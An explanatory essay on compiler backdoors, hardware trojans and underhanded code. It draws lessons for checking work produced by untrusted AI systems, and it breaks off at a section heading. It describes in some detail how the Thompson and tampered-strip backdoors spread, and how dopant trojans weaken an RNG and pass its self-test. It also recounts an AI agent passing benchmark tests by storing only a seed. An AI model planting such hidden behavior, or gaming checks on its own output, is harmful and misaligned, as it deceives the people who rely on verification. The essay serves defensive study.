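# Compiler backdoors, hardware trojans and underhanded code: what they show about verifying outputs

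## How an artifact can pass its check and still hide behavior

A compiler translates the code programmers write into instructions a machine can run. A compiler backdoor is a change that makes the compiler insert malicious behavior into the programs it builds. A hardware trojan is a malicious change to a chip's design or manufacture. Underhanded code is source code that looks innocent to a reviewer but does something malicious. Programmers and engineers have built working examples of each, the oldest in the 1970s, and many passed the inspections and tests that users ordinarily rely on.

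AI safety researchers cite these cases because one proposal for using an AI system that nobody fully trusts is to accept its work whenever the work passes a check. Backdoors, trojans and underhanded code show how such checks perform when the producer is a person with something to hide.

### Producer, checker and specification

In all of these cases, a producer makes an artifact, such as a program, a compiler, a chip or an AI model. A checker, which may be a person, a test or a tool, compares the artifact with a specification, the list of properties it ought to have, and accepts or rejects it. The producer decides whatever the specification leaves open. This is usually harmless. For example, a customer who wants a list sorted does not care which sorting method the programmer picks. But a producer with bad intentions can use the same freedom to hide behavior in an artifact that passes its check.

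Krentsel, Agarwal and colleagues (2026), in *Reality Is the Final Verifier*, put the arrangement into symbols. Their evaluator E (the checker) accepts an implementation P (the artifact) when

E(P, R, M) = pass,

where R stands for the recorded requirements and M for a model of the environment in which P will run. Two things that matter are missing from the formula. One is what the people who ordered the artifact actually want, which R only approximates. The other is the real world, which M only approximates. A mathematical proof that P meets R under M leaves both approximations exactly as rough as they were.

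In their main example, which involves no malice, an AI agent was asked to speed up a key-value store, a simple database that keeps a value under each name. The benchmark filled the store with predictable values generated from a seed, so the agent's version saved only the seed and recomputed each value on request. Throughput rose about sixfold, and the new version passed every correctness test. The researchers admit that they had not thought to specify that a store must keep the values its users give it.

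For a small enough task, the specification can be exact. An 8-bit adder, for example, must output (x + y) mod 256 for every pair of 8-bit inputs, and a checker can try all 65,536 pairs. Even then, as Krentsel and colleagues point out, the result covers only that property. It doesn't cover how long the circuit takes, how much power it draws, what it does when hot or how it behaves after a fault, unless someone adds those to the specification.

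### Source code, binaries and compilers

Programmers write source code in a language such as C, and a compiler translates it into a binary, a file of machine instructions that a processor can run. Reviewing the source code therefore helps someone who runs the binary only if the compiler translated it faithfully. The reviewer can also read the compiler's source code, but the compiler that did the translation is itself a binary, produced by an earlier compiler.

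Often the earlier compiler is an older copy of the same one. Many compilers are written in the language they compile, such as a C compiler written in C, so once a first version has been built some other way, each version can build the next. The binary of such a compiler can contain facts that appear nowhere in its source. *Running the “Reflections on Trusting Trust” Compiler* (Cox, 2023) retells a harmless example. In C, a programmer types the two characters `\n` for a line break, which the machine stores as the number 10. At first, the compiler's source has to state that `\n` produces 10. After building and installing that version, the compiler's author replaces the rule with a neater one, which states that `\n` produces `\n`, and the 10 no longer appears in the source. The new rule looks circular, but it works because the installed binary already contains the number and copies it into the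 next binary, which does the same in turn.

In his Turing Award lecture, *Reflections on Trusting Trust*, Unix co-creator Ken Thompson described how he used the same inheritance to pass on a backdoor. He concluded that people cannot trust code they did not wholly create themselves. Krentsel and colleagues apply this conclusion to software from AI agents, and Roesner and Kohno (2026), in *Reflections on Trusting Trust, Revisited*, extend it to coding agents that write their own next versions.

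### Who holds a chip design at each stage

More parties handle a chip design than handle a program. *Formal Security Guarantees for Trustworthy Hardware Supply Chains* (Sisejkovic, Reimann and colleagues, 2023) follows the design from one company to the next, and *Trojan Scanner* (Asadi) places testing between fabrication and assembly.

| Stage | Form of the design | Who holds it |
|---|---|---|
| Specification and design | Written goals, then code in a hardware language | Design owner, using some blocks from outside vendors |
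| Logic synthesis | Netlist: the logic gates and their connections | Design owner or an external design house |
| Physical design | Layout: the position and wiring of every transistor | Design owner or an external design house |
| Fabrication | Masks, wafers, then bare chips | Foundry |
| Testing | Finished chips under test patterns | Often the foundry or another outside company |
| Assembly and sale | Packaged chips on circuit boards | Assembly firms, then the brand that sells the device |

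The code at the top of the table reads much like software. It describes, in a language such as Verilog, which values move between the chip's registers (small internal stores) on each clock tick. Design tools turn this code into a netlist and the netlist into a layout. Their role is roughly that of a compiler, and they raise the same worry that the tool could insert hidden behavior. The chip's owner typically licenses these tools from other companies as closed products. If the owner uses an external design house, that company usually also adds the test circuitry that a tester will later use to read the chip's internal state.

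An advanced chip plant costs billions of dollars, so most design companies own none and lose much of their control over a chip when an outside foundry makes it. According to *Detecting Hardware Trojans Inserted by Untrusted Foundry using Physical Inspection*, by Vashistha, Rahman and colleagues, the foundry has full access to the layout, the netlist and the test vectors, which are the input patterns for the production tests. A dishonest foundry would therefore know in advance how the chip will be tested. It could fit extra gates into unused space on the chip, swap out filler cells that do no computing, or thin a wire so that the chip fails early. The attacker could also act without the foundry management's involvement, since *Hardware Trojans from Invisible Inversions* (2026) includes rogue process engineers and people who intercept the design files on their way to the plant among those who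 could alter a chip.

It is unclear how often anyone has done this. In January 2023, Sisejkovic and colleagues knew of no confirmed hardware trojan outside the laboratory, but added that a company that found one might well keep quiet to protect its business.

### Three ways past a check

Engineers divide a hardware trojan into two parts, which apply equally well to software. The trigger is the input or condition that switches the hidden behavior on. The payload is what that behavior does, such as leaking a key or shutting the device down. A producer can hide the payload from inspection by choosing a trigger that no test supplies, because the artifact behaves exactly as specified until the trigger arrives. *An Automated Framework for Generating Stealthy Cell-Embedded Hardware Trojans* (2026) lists the usual choices: rare input patterns, rare values on internal wires, and long sequences of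 events. Ordinary simulation, random tests and production tests may never produce any of them. Sisejkovic and colleagues add sensor readings and radio signals that an antenna on the chip picks up.

Triggers that depend on a sequence of operations are especially hard for a checker to catch. Suppose an 8-bit adder contains a hidden counter and adds correctly a trillion times before it starts to give wrong answers. A checker who tries all 65,536 input pairs will find every answer right, because the trigger depends on how many additions the device has already done rather than on which numbers it adds.

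Some trojans have no trigger and run as soon as the power comes on. They pass because the specification doesn't cover what they do. *When AI Writes the World’s Software, Who Verifies It?* (2026) describes a hypothetical AI system that rewrites a TLS library, the code that encrypts web traffic. The new version passes every test, but one branch in it depends on bits of the secret key. Its outputs are all correct, but its running time varies slightly with the key, so an attacker who measures it can work out part of the key.

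A weakened random-number generator can also pass its tests. Tech Design Forum's *Hardware trojan attacks and countermeasures* describes very simple trojans that lower the effective entropy, or unpredictability, of the generator in an encryption chip. For example, a generator might secretly derive each 128-bit key from a 32-bit number. If the derivation method is good, the keys will pass statistical tests for randomness, but an attacker who knows the method has only about 4.3 billion candidates to try, which takes a few seconds at a billion per second.

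More tests of the listed properties would not catch either fault. Someone has to think of the missing property and add it to the list. *When AI Writes the World’s Software, Who Verifies It?* recommends mathematical proof, on the ground that a proof covers all inputs and no producer can game it. That holds only for the properties stated in the theorem. Trying to prove that the library runs in constant time would expose the leaking branch, but someone would first have to ask for constant time. *Zero-Trust Formal Methods* (2026) describes a real case in which AI agents wrote programs to check the answers of automated solvers. A proof tool had verified one of these programs, but the part that reported its result could still print the wrong verdict. Independent review and further testing caught this and similar faults. The paper concludes that the specifications matter most and that no tool can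 check them, so human reviewers have to.

Tampering can also happen after the stage being checked. A reviewer may read clean source code before an altered compiler adds a payload to the binary, or a design owner may verify the hardware code before the foundry changes the layout. Even a flawless check of the source or design would miss this, because the user receives something different from what the checker examined. The checker has to examine the later stage directly or show that it matches the earlier one.

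Krentsel and colleagues use nearly the same categories. They place a missed trigger in the "evaluation gap", where the artifact breaks a stated requirement and the evaluator fails to notice, and an omitted property in the "requirement gap". Their "model gap" includes mismatches between source code and what runs, but also much else, such as unanticipated workloads. They argue that a sound proof can close the evaluation gap once the requirements and the model are fixed, but that nobody can certify that the other two gaps are closed in an open and changing world.

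Real attacks often combine these routes. A trojan added at the foundry avoids every check on the design, but it still has to pass the tests on finished chips, so it usually needs a trigger as well. Thompson's backdoor entered through the compiler and acted only when the compiler processed particular programs. Underhanded code carries a different risk for the attacker, because the reviewer can see the whole program and the attack works only if they misjudge what a line does.

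### A payload behind one 64-bit value

Some arithmetic shows how cheaply a trigger can defeat testing. Suppose a program takes a 64-bit number as input and handles every value correctly except one, which runs the payload. There are 2^64 possible values, about 1.8 × 10^19. The checker does not know the special one and feeds in random values at a billion a second. A year has about 3.2 × 10^7 seconds, so after a year the checker has run about 3.2 × 10^16 tests. Repeats are so rare at this scale that they hardly matter, and the chance of having hit the trigger is close to

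3.2 × 10^16 / 1.8 × 10^19 ≈ 0.17%.

A year of testing without an alarm is very weak evidence that the program contains no such trigger. A checker who started with an estimate of 50% should lower it only to about 49.96%. The same test rig would take about a thousandth of a second, on average, to hit an accidental bug that shows up on one input in a million. Random testing works well against accidental bugs because nobody placed them to avoid it. *When AI Writes the World's Software, Who Verifies It?* notes that a determined adversary can study the test suite and plant bugs that evade it.

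Adding hardware gives the checker limited help, because the producer can lengthen the trigger and each extra bit doubles the checker's work. One machine would take about 585 years to go through all the 64-bit values in order. A million machines would take about five hours, and a wealthy customer who was worried enough could pay for them. But lengthening the trigger to 128 bits takes the producer only a few more gates or one more line of code, and it raises the time for the same million machines to around 10^16 years.

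These figures assume a checker who can only supply inputs and watch outputs. A checker who can also look inside the artifact could easily spot a comparison with a fixed 64-bit constant in the source code. A coverage tool, which records the lines that ran during testing, would also flag the payload as code that no test had reached. A producer who expects these checks has to disguise the trigger or insert it at a stage where nobody will look.

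## Demonstrations in compilers and build tools

### The Air Force evaluation of Multics

In *Multics Security Evaluation Vulnerability Analysis* (June 1974), two US Air Force officers, Karger and Schell, reported on their attempts to break into Multics, a time-sharing operating system that the Air Force hoped to use for Secret and Top Secret work on the same machine. They explained how an intruder could leave a "trap door", a hidden way back in. The best place for it was the binary of a system program, where nobody would find it by reading the source code, but recompiling the program would remove it.

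The officers had met this problem in practice. *Thirty Years Later* (Karger and Schell, 2002) reprints the original report, which describes how they first hid a trap door in a Multics procedure that the maintainers were about to modify and recompile. They had to move it to another procedure, and the new version responded only to a 72-bit password. Such a password has 256 times as many possible values as the 64-bit trigger described earlier, so ordinary testing had no realistic chance of setting off the trap door.

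An intruder could get around recompilation by tampering with the compiler instead. Most of the Multics supervisor, the privileged core of the system, was written in PL/I. A tampered PL/I compiler could detect when it was compiling part of the supervisor and add a trap door to the binary. The compiler was also written in PL/I, so it could do the same to its own next version, and the trap door would survive even if someone recompiled the whole system. Karger and Schell added in a footnote that an assembler, which translates a lower-level language, would work just as well.

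They estimated the cost at perhaps five times that of the attacks they had carried out. Their simple trap door had taken at most 18 hours of work and $80 of computer time, and all their attacks together at most 257 hours and $1,560. Five times the larger figures is about 1,300 hours and $7,800. They wrote that a foreign agent would consider costs several hundred times those in their table nominal.

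Karger and Schell described the compiler trap door in only a few lines of their report and did not build it, but they did test whether a manufacturer would ship a simpler one. At MIT, they planted a harmless version, one instruction away from being malicious, in the software for the next Multics machine, the Honeywell 6180. Honeywell then delivered it to a computer in the Pentagon. The published report contained a hint about this trap door, but nobody found it for about another year, until it returned an odd error code during a security audit at General Motors. According to Multicians, a website on the history of Multics, nobody ever discovered a back door in a 6180 system. Karger and Schell's account is first-hand and more detailed, and the two accounts may disagree only about whether a harmless back door counts.

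### Thompson's three steps

Thompson built a compiler trap door after reading about the idea in the Air Force report. In his Turing Award lecture, given in October 1983 and published in August 1984, he could no longer identify the report and asked readers for the reference. Karger and Schell gave him a new copy.

*Reflections on Trusting Trust* builds up the attack in three steps, starting with a program that prints its own source code. A tampered compiler needs this ability because it has to give its successor the code that does the tampering, and the successor has to be able to pass that code on again. Storing a copy inside the program seems to lead nowhere, since the copy would have to contain another copy, and so on without end. The way out is to use one piece of text twice, as in this English sentence:

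Write out the following, then write it out again in quotation marks: "Write out the following, then write it out again in quotation marks:"

A self-reproducing program outputs a complete copy of its own source code, including the instructions that produce the copy. Thompson pointed out that such a program can carry any amount of extra text, which it copies along with the rest. In his compiler attack, the extra text is the backdoor.

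The second step is the inheritance described earlier, in which a compiler's binary contains a fact missing from its source. Thompson's example was the number that stands for a vertical tab, which works the same way as the line break.

The third step replaces the harmless number with two pieces of malicious code. The first recognizes the source of `login`, the Unix program that checks passwords, and makes the compiled version accept an extra password known to the attacker. Anyone who read the compiler's source would soon notice this code, so the second piece recognizes the source of the compiler and inserts both pieces into the new binary. The attacker compiles the altered source once, installs the result as the official compiler, and restores the clean source. Every compiler and every copy of `login` that people then build from clean source with this binary contains the backdoor.

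### The code from 1975

In March 2023, Thompson told an audience in California that he still had the program and that nobody had ever asked him for it. Cox, a programmer who worked on the Go language, asked for it that September and published the code with notes in October. The code is 99 lines of C and a 20-line script, in files dated June 1975.

Thompson put the backdoor in the preprocessor, the part of the compiler that reads the source text first. The added code skips any tabs at the start of each line and compares the next 21 characters with a statement in `login` that scrambles the password a user typed. If they match, it adds a few instructions to the end of the line, and these make `login` accept the password "codenih" for any existing account.

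To recognize the compiler, the code needs three matches in order:

1. a line that is distinctive to the compiler's source
2. the start of the loop that reads the input
3. the instruction that writes out the last of the output

The order matters because the reading loop is ordinary, and other programs may contain the same text. After the second match, the backdoor adds an instruction to run its line-by-line check in the new compiler. After the third, it adds an instruction to run its copying routine. At the end of the file, it writes out its own complete source, so the new compiler contains everything the old one did.

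Here the program uses the self-reproducing trick. It stores its own text as a list of numbers, one for each character, with a marker where the list belongs. To copy itself, it prints the text before the marker, then the list as numbers, then the text after the marker. The 20-line script creates the list the first time.

Thompson also made the backdoor inactive when a programmer used the option for viewing the preprocessor's output, so anyone who checked that output would have seen clean code.

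Cox ran the program in an emulator of Unix's Sixth Edition. The ordinary compiler was 10,724 bytes and the tampered one 12,918, about 20% more. When he compiled the same clean compiler source with each, the output was the same size as the compiler that produced it. The tampered compiler's output differed from the tampered compiler in six bytes, because the compiler had stored the name of the source file, and the next generation matched exactly. Cox installed the tampered compiler, rebuilt the compiler and `login` from clean source, and logged in as the system's administrator with the password "codenih".

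He had imagined a backdoor that analyzed the structure of programs deep inside the compiler, and was surprised that replacing text was enough. Anyone with a clean binary of the same version could have caught the backdoor by comparing sizes, since the clean binary is 10,724 bytes and the tampered one is 12,918. But a user with only the tampered binary gets 12,918 bytes at every rebuild and has no reason to expect a different size.

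The attack also works on modern compilers. Cox altered the Go compiler's routine for reading source files so that a program meant to print "hello, world" printed "backdoored!" instead. After he removed the alteration from the source and rebuilt the compiler, the new compiler still produced a program that printed "backdoored!". Skrimstad also built a self-copying attack on the Go compiler in a thesis at the University of Oslo.

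### How the backdoor fared at Bell Labs

Thompson also let colleagues in the Programmer's Workbench group (PWB), which ran its own Unix systems at Bell Labs, use the tampered compiler without telling them what it did. Doug McIlroy, another Unix veteran, recalled that someone at PWB noticed an experimental compiler on the research group's machine and took it. Thompson said in 2023 that he "got somebody to steal it" in a controlled way.

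John Mashey, who used one of the PWB systems, explained in a November 1982 message why the group accepted a binary. The C compiler was changing so quickly that an old version often could not compile the newest source, so users had to copy the new source and binary together. Mashey thought this helped the trap considerably. His message is one of two on the subject that Plotnick (1983) reposted from an archive in *Need trojan horse info*.

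A mistake by Thompson gave the backdoor away. Thompson (2021), in *Thompson trojan put into practice*, recalled that PWB recompiled the compiler twice and found it one byte larger each time. The group kept experimenting until it broke the part that copied the backdoor, and Thompson was not sure that anyone there ever understood what had happened. According to Cox, each generation added a stray zero to the end of the stored text. He adds that binaries on that system always had an even length, so the file must actually have grown by two bytes at every second rebuild. Thompson did not keep the faulty version, and the code he released does not have the bug.

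Mashey remembered a different clue, which was that the compiler's symbol table, a list of the functions and variables in the binary, contained a name that appeared nowhere in the source. Linderman (2021), also in *Thompson trojan put into practice*, remembered that Larry Wehr had listed the symbols, possibly because of the extra byte. The two clues are compatible, and both men thought PWB might never have noticed if Thompson had not put the extra code in its own function.

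The accounts disagree about how the backdoor ended. Dennis Ritchie, who worked with Thompson on Unix, gave the earliest one in *Joy of reproduction* (1982), a year before the lecture. He wrote that the backdoor lasted several months, until someone copied a preprocessor binary from another system, and promised that no distributed version of Unix had ever contained such a backdoor. CNCF's *"Unix Support Group" event*, an entry in a catalogue of software attacks, lists another Bell Labs group as the target, but a message from Mashey, who was a user at PWB, supports Cox's version.

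These are recollections, some of them more than 45 years old, and they can't establish how much PWB understood. But they agree that the evidence was in the binary, since the size and the symbol table are both properties of it, and nobody claims to have found the backdoor by reading source code. Thompson could have avoided leaving this evidence, so PWB's success is little guide to the chances of catching a more careful attacker.

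### When the source code changes

A backdoor that matches text can also stop working even if no one is looking for it. If a maintainer of `login` renames a variable, or even changes the spacing, in the line that Thompson's code matches, the next `login` will be compiled without the backdoor.

Changes to the compiler's source can disable the backdoor, and the effect depends on which of the three lines changes. If a maintainer rewrites the first line, the search never starts. The next compiler comes out clean without any error message, so users never learn that they had a backdoor. If the maintainer rewrites only the third line, the backdoor still adds a call to its line-by-line check but never adds the code for that check. The build should then fail with an error about a missing function, and the function's name would be a good place to start an investigation.

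An attacker can reduce this risk by including several patterns or by supplying a fresh tampered binary from time to time. Users at Bell Labs already fetched a new binary whenever the compiler changed too much, which would have helped an attacker. Still, the longest recorded run of Thompson's backdoor is the several months that Ritchie mentioned. Thompson showed that the copying works, but not whether a backdoor of this kind could survive decades of maintenance by other people.

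### Tampering with strip

Malka, Sharma and colleagues (2026), in *Trusting-Trust Attack against an Entire Linux Distribution through Binary Manipulation*, removed the attack's dependence on source text. They tampered with strip, a standard tool that removes information a finished binary doesn't need to run, such as its symbol table. Strip neither reads nor produces source code.

They targeted NixOS, a version of Linux whose packages come with exact recipes for building them from source. NixOS gets its first build tools from a bootstrap seed of about twenty ready-made programs, including a compiler and strip. It uses these to rebuild its tools from source in several stages. The final tools, which NixOS calls its standard environment, no longer refer to the seed when they run.

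The researchers replaced strip in the seed and left all the recipes and source code unchanged. A real attacker would have to break into the system that produces or publishes the seed, or persuade the maintainers to accept a tampered one. The experiment starts after this step, with the tampered seed already in place.

According to Malka and colleagues, a build tool can pass on its own tampering if three conditions hold:

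- The build relies on a ready-made copy of the tool before it builds the tool from source.
- An earlier copy of the tool modifies the newly built copy.
- The modified copy later performs the same operation in other builds.

In NixOS, strip meets all three conditions. By default, every package build ends by running strip on the finished programs. When the package is strip itself, the old copy runs on the new one, and a tampered old copy can add its payload to it.

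The payload sits in an added part of the program file and leaves the program's own code unchanged. When someone starts the program, the payload runs first and then hands control to the original code. It spreads only when the program is strip, by copying itself into every suitable file that strip is about to trim. It prints nothing during package builds, but on a user's machine it prints a short message, which stands in for an attack such as stealing passwords.

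Malka and colleagues used the tampered seed to build the NixOS graphical installer, a set of 1,199 packages, and every build succeeded. The installer contained 3,799 programs that a user can start, 3,791 of them from the command line. Of these, 3,790 printed the message, including `sudo`, which gives a user administrator rights, and programs written in several languages, including Rust and Go. Because `strip` processes finished binaries, tampering with it can affect programs in all these languages, whereas a tampered C compiler would affect only programs in the languages it compiles.

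The exception was Firefox, whose build recipe skips `strip`. The researchers also ran the installer's functional tests, which operate a desktop and install the system from scratch on a virtual machine. These tests checked whether the programs still worked, and none failed.

| | Thompson's compiler | Tampered strip |
|---|---|---|
| Normal job | Translates source code | Trims finished binaries |
| How the backdoor reaches the next copy | The old compiler compiles the new one | The old strip trims the new one |
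| What the backdoor looks for | Exact lines of source text | The name of the program it is running in |
| Programs it altered | The compiler and `login` | Nearly every program in the installer |
| What stops it | A change to a matched line | A build that skips strip |

The payload goes into every suitable file, so it doesn't need to identify the next version of strip. Programmers could completely rewrite strip's source, and the new version would still pick up the payload as long as an infected copy trimmed it. The attack depends on the format of the binary rather than on the source. The prototype can't handle shared libraries, other processor types or some less common kinds of program file, though Malka and colleagues regard these as limits of the prototype and not of the method. Some other Linux distributions don't run strip by default, so the attack might not carry over to them directly.

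The experiment covers a single run of the bootstrap on one version of the package collection, and it didn't test detection. The researchers deliberately made the payload easy to find, with a visible message and a labeled section in each infected file, and they asked nobody to look for it. They argue that an attacker could let the payload spread only from one strip to the next, perhaps for years, and activate it once it reached the intended target. That would leave far fewer infected files to find, but each new strip would still contain code that doesn't come from its source.

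Malka and colleagues then checked the other tools that the default build steps in NixOS call directly by name, nearly forty in all. One of them, patchelf, meets all three conditions because it adjusts the library paths in newly built programs, including new copies of itself. The tools install and cp are plausible carriers because they copy finished programs into place. The researchers rule out others, such as make and tar, because they don't normally rewrite finished programs. But a tampered tool can do more than its normal work. A malicious make runs during the same builds and could alter a new copy of itself if it has permission to change the output. The three conditions are better read as a guide to which tools could hide the tampering inside an operation they already perform.

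Thompson predicted this kind of attack in his lecture, saying he could have picked any program that handles programs, such as an assembler or a loader. Karger and Schell had already mentioned assemblers. Malka and colleagues built a working attack and measured its reach. If a second person rebuilds NixOS from the same tampered seed to check the first build, both should get the same infected files, so a match would prove nothing about the seed. A smaller seed would give an attacker fewer binaries to tamper with. It is disputed whether a comparison through a second compiler would catch the attack.

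### How far Thompson's moral holds

Thompson concluded that "no amount of source-level verification or scrutiny" protects people who use untrusted code, and for these attacks that is correct. The source of `login`, the C compiler and strip was clean in the final stage of each demonstration, so even a perfect reviewer would have been right to approve it. Rebuilding from the approved source would not have helped as long as the build used the tampered tool.

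The moral is about checks on source code, but a checker can also examine the binary. The PWB group noticed the growing file and the unexplained symbol without knowing what to look for. In Cox's emulator, a comparison with a clean compiler's output exposed the backdoor immediately. Wheeler argues in *Fully Countering Trusting Trust through Diverse Double-Compiling (DDC)* that the real problem was that users had no practical way to verify independently that a binary corresponds to its source. He does not see trust itself as the problem, because everyone in a modern society has to rely on other people. Once users can verify that the binary and source correspond, reading the source becomes useful again, because it tells them what the binary does.

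The demonstrations also don't show how common such backdoors are. In each, someone could already put a tampered binary where others would use it. Thompson could do this at Bell Labs because his colleagues already got their compilers from his group. Attackers have also spread malicious compilers, including in the XcodeGhost and W32/Induc cases that Skrimstad discusses. But Cox points out that attackers usually have much easier options, since programmers routinely download and run strangers' source code that almost nobody has checked.

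Thompson's other advice, to trust only code that you "totally" created yourself, is hard to follow. If a programmer wrote a new `login` from scratch, Thompson's compiler would probably leave it unchanged, because the new source is unlikely to contain the exact line that the backdoor looks for. The tampered `strip` would still add its payload, regardless of who wrote the program or what its source looks like. To be safe under Thompson's rule, the programmer would also have to write the compiler, `strip` and every other tool that handles the binary, as well as the microcode, the built-in instructions that control the processor, which Thompson also named as a place to hide a bug.

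## Demonstrations in chips

A programmer who wrote every tool and all the microcode would still run them on a chip that other people designed and made. A backdoor in the chip's circuits can give an attacker control of a machine even when its software is clean in both source and binary. Researchers have demonstrated this with extra logic gates, chemical changes to existing transistors, and a single added cell that stores electric charge.

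### Extra gates in a processor

In *Designing and implementing malicious hardware* (2008), King, Tucek and colleagues altered the hardware code of the Leon3, an open-source processor. An attacker who did the same would need access to the design, for example as an employee or a vendor of design blocks. The researchers loaded the altered design onto an FPGA, a chip that users can configure to act as almost any digital circuit, and ran Linux on it.

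An earlier trojan from IBM used 406 gates to leak RSA encryption keys in simulation, and it could do nothing else. King and colleagues wanted hardware that would support many attacks, so they built two general mechanisms and left the details of each attack to software.

One mechanism switches off memory protection, which stops ordinary programs from reading or changing the operating system's data. The added circuit checks the bytes entering the processor for a preset sequence, which can be as long as the attacker likes. A program that loads this sequence can then search the operating system's memory for the record of its own process and give itself administrator rights. The attacker must first get a program onto the machine, but that program needs no special rights.

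The other mechanism, "shadow mode", runs hidden instructions from a reserved part of the cache, the processor's fast internal memory. The attacker sends the machine a network packet that the operating system will discard, but only after computing its checksum, which passes the packet's bytes through the processor. The added circuit detects the trigger and loads the packet's contents as a hidden program. This program waits for someone to log in with the password "letmein", makes the password check succeed, and then removes itself. This has the same effect as Thompson's backdoor, but no file on the disk contains the hidden program.

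| Design | Logic gates | Gates added | Lines of hardware code added |
|---|---|---|---|
| Original Leon3 | 1,787,958 | | |
| With the memory mechanism | 1,788,917 | 959 (0.05%) | 68 |
| With shadow mode | 1,789,299 | 1,341 (0.08%) | 117 |

The trojans add only a very small percentage of gates, but someone reviewing the design reads code. Shadow mode adds about 1% to the original's 11,195 lines. King and colleagues did not report asking anyone to look for it.

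They also didn't put the processor through a manufacturer's tests. They argue that such tests would fail because a tester can try only a tiny fraction of the states a processor can be in. Sixteen 32-bit registers and 80 kilobytes of cache hold 655,872 bits, which allows 2^655,872 combinations. As with the 64-bit trigger described earlier, this argument doesn't apply to a tester who can also look inside and see which parts of the design the tests never used.

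The group measured how much the login attack slowed five benchmark programs. The programs ran 1.34% slower when an attacker used the backdoor to log in and copy the password file, and 1.32% slower when someone who knew the real password did the same on an unaltered processor. If the attacker left the backdoor active all the time, the slowdown rose to 13%, because ordinary programs lost part of the cache. The larger slowdown matters for another attack in the paper, which must stay active to steal users' passwords. King and colleagues ran that attack only in a simulator.

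The altered processor ran on an FPGA, so nobody had to manufacture it, but Hepp and Sigl sent a microcontroller design containing four trojans to be made into a chip. *CRESS* (2026), which proposes a way to score hardware attacks, examines one of these trojans, which leaks data through the chip's power use or electromagnetic emissions. The paper assumes that the attacker is the company that supplies the base design. According to *CRESS*, the attacker also has to modify the compiler that builds software for the chip.

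Most public examples of hardware trojans are much smaller than commercial chips. So Popryho, Pal and Partin-Vaisband (2025), in *Automated Hardware Trojan Insertion in Industrial-Scale Designs*, wrote software that adds trojan-like circuits to industrial-size netlists without changing what the chip does. The machine-learning detectors they tried failed to find these circuits.

### Changed doping in a random number generator

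Foundries would struggle to copy King's attack. They usually have only the layout, so they would have to find room for over a thousand gates and connect them around the existing wires. A customer could then photograph the chip's layers and see the additions. In *Stealthy Dopant-Level Hardware Trojans*, Becker, Regazzoni and colleagues (2013) looked for a change that a foundry could make without adding gates or wires.

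One demonstration made a hardware trojan by changing the doping of transistors. Manufacturers dope silicon by adding traces of other elements, which creates two kinds of region, n-type and p-type, and a transistor works because of the way these regions meet. In an inverter, the simplest logic gate, one transistor can connect the output to the supply voltage, which stands for 1, and another can connect it to ground, which stands for 0. Replacing the p-type doping in the first transistor with n-type permanently connects the output to the supply. Reversing the doping at one contact of the second disconnects the output from ground. The gate then outputs 1 regardless of its input, while its wires and the outlines of its transistors look unchanged.

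The researchers applied this to a design derived from the random number generator in Intel's Ivy Bridge processors. The generator collects electrical noise and uses it to fill two 128-bit registers, K and c. To produce a random number r, it adds 1 to c and computes

r = AES_K(c),

where AES is a standard encryption algorithm and K serves as its key. Normally, an attacker knows neither register. The trojan fixes all 128 bits of K and all but n bits of c at values the attacker has chosen, so r depends on only n unknown bits. With n = 32, the attacker has the same 4.3 billion candidates to try as in the weakened generator described earlier.

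The change affects 4 of the 32 transistors in each altered flip-flop, a circuit that stores one bit. For n = 32, the attacker has to alter 224 flip-flops, or 896 transistors. The trojan has no trigger and weakens every number the generator produces.

With n = 32, the output passed every test in the random-number suite published by NIST, the US standards agency, because AES turns even nearly identical inputs into outputs that seem unrelated. A simple search for repeated values should detect the tampering, since there are only 4.3 billion possible outputs and a sample of one million should contain over a hundred repeats. An unmodified 128-bit generator would almost certainly produce none. The attacker could make repeats rarer by choosing a larger n, but would then have more candidates to try.

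#### How the trojan passed the self-test

The generator also tests itself each time the power comes on. It disconnects the noise source, feeds in a fixed stream of bits, and collects four outputs, 512 bits in all. It reduces these to a 32-bit checksum and compares that with a value stored in the chip. An altered generator produces the wrong outputs, but it still passes if their checksum matches the stored value.

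The test input never changes, so the attacker can calculate the expected checksum in advance. The checksum is short enough that any choice of constants for K and c has a 1 in 2^32 chance of producing it, so the attacker can simulate choices until one matches. At a million tries per second, 2^32 tries take about 72 minutes.

With n = 32, the attacker can set 224 bits freely, and about 2^192 of the 2^224 possible choices should pass. If the chip compared all 512 output bits instead, the probability that even one choice would pass would be roughly 1 in 2^288. Changing the input at every test would also help, because constants that match on one input would almost certainly fail on the next, but the chip would then need a trustworthy way to work out the right answer each time.

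The self-test still catches ordinary manufacturing faults with the trojan in place, because a random fault is very unlikely to produce the right checksum. A cruder attack would disable the test's error signal, but Becker and colleagues point out that a test that never reported a defect would look suspicious.

Intel relied on the self-test for security reasons. An attacker could use a chip's ordinary test circuitry to read the generator's secrets, so Intel left that circuitry out. Leaving it out also removed a check that might have exposed the fixed registers.

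Becker and colleagues did not alter an Intel processor in this work, and they describe no manufactured chip. In the slides for their 2013 talk, they suggest that the main practical difficulties are reverse-engineering the design and learning how the manufacturer tests it. The foundry needs to know both to carry out this attack.

#### Correct outputs that leak a key

The same paper describes a second trojan, which leaves every output correct. It alters part of an AES circuit designed to hide its power use, because an attacker who measures a chip's power can sometimes work out its encryption key. The researchers changed the doping in two gates so that one combination of data values draws nearly twice the normal energy, about 120 femtojoules instead of 67. In simulated power measurements, someone who knew about this pattern could easily pick out the correct key. The common power attacks the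 researchers tried worked no better on the altered circuit than on the original.

As with the TLS library described earlier, testing the answers can't expose the leak. A checker would have to measure the power and know roughly what pattern to look for.

#### Making the doping visible

Becker and colleagues also expected inspection to fail, because ordinary images of a chip do not show the type of doping. A year later, *Reversing Stealthy Dopant-Level Circuits* (Sugawara, Suzuki and colleagues, 2014) showed that an electron microscope can reveal the doping type.

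Researchers polished a chip down to its contact layer, where the wiring meets the silicon, and examined it under a microscope. The microscope's beam knocks electrons out of each contact, leaving it positively charged unless the silicon below can replace them. A contact connected to a large conducting region regains electrons quickly and appears bright, while one with a poor supply stays charged, pulls some of the escaping electrons back and appears dark. The type of doping affects the brightness because it determines which regions connect. All four combinations of doping and surrounding silicon looked different at high magnification.

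The chip in this experiment used the same principle as Becker's trojan, but for a legitimate purpose, to hide a company's circuits from competitors. Its features were also much larger, at 180 nanometers compared with 45 in Becker's cell library, and the researchers knew where the altered cells were. The result shows that the doping can be seen, but it does not measure how often an inspector would find a few hundred altered transistors among millions.

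Distinguishing all four combinations also takes up to 16 times as many images as inspecting a metal layer. In the slides for the talk, the researchers estimate that 77 images would cover one AES circuit at the lower magnification, so the higher magnification could require more than 1,200. Polishing destroys the chip, so a customer can inspect a sample this way but not the chips that will go into use.

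### A capacitor that counts

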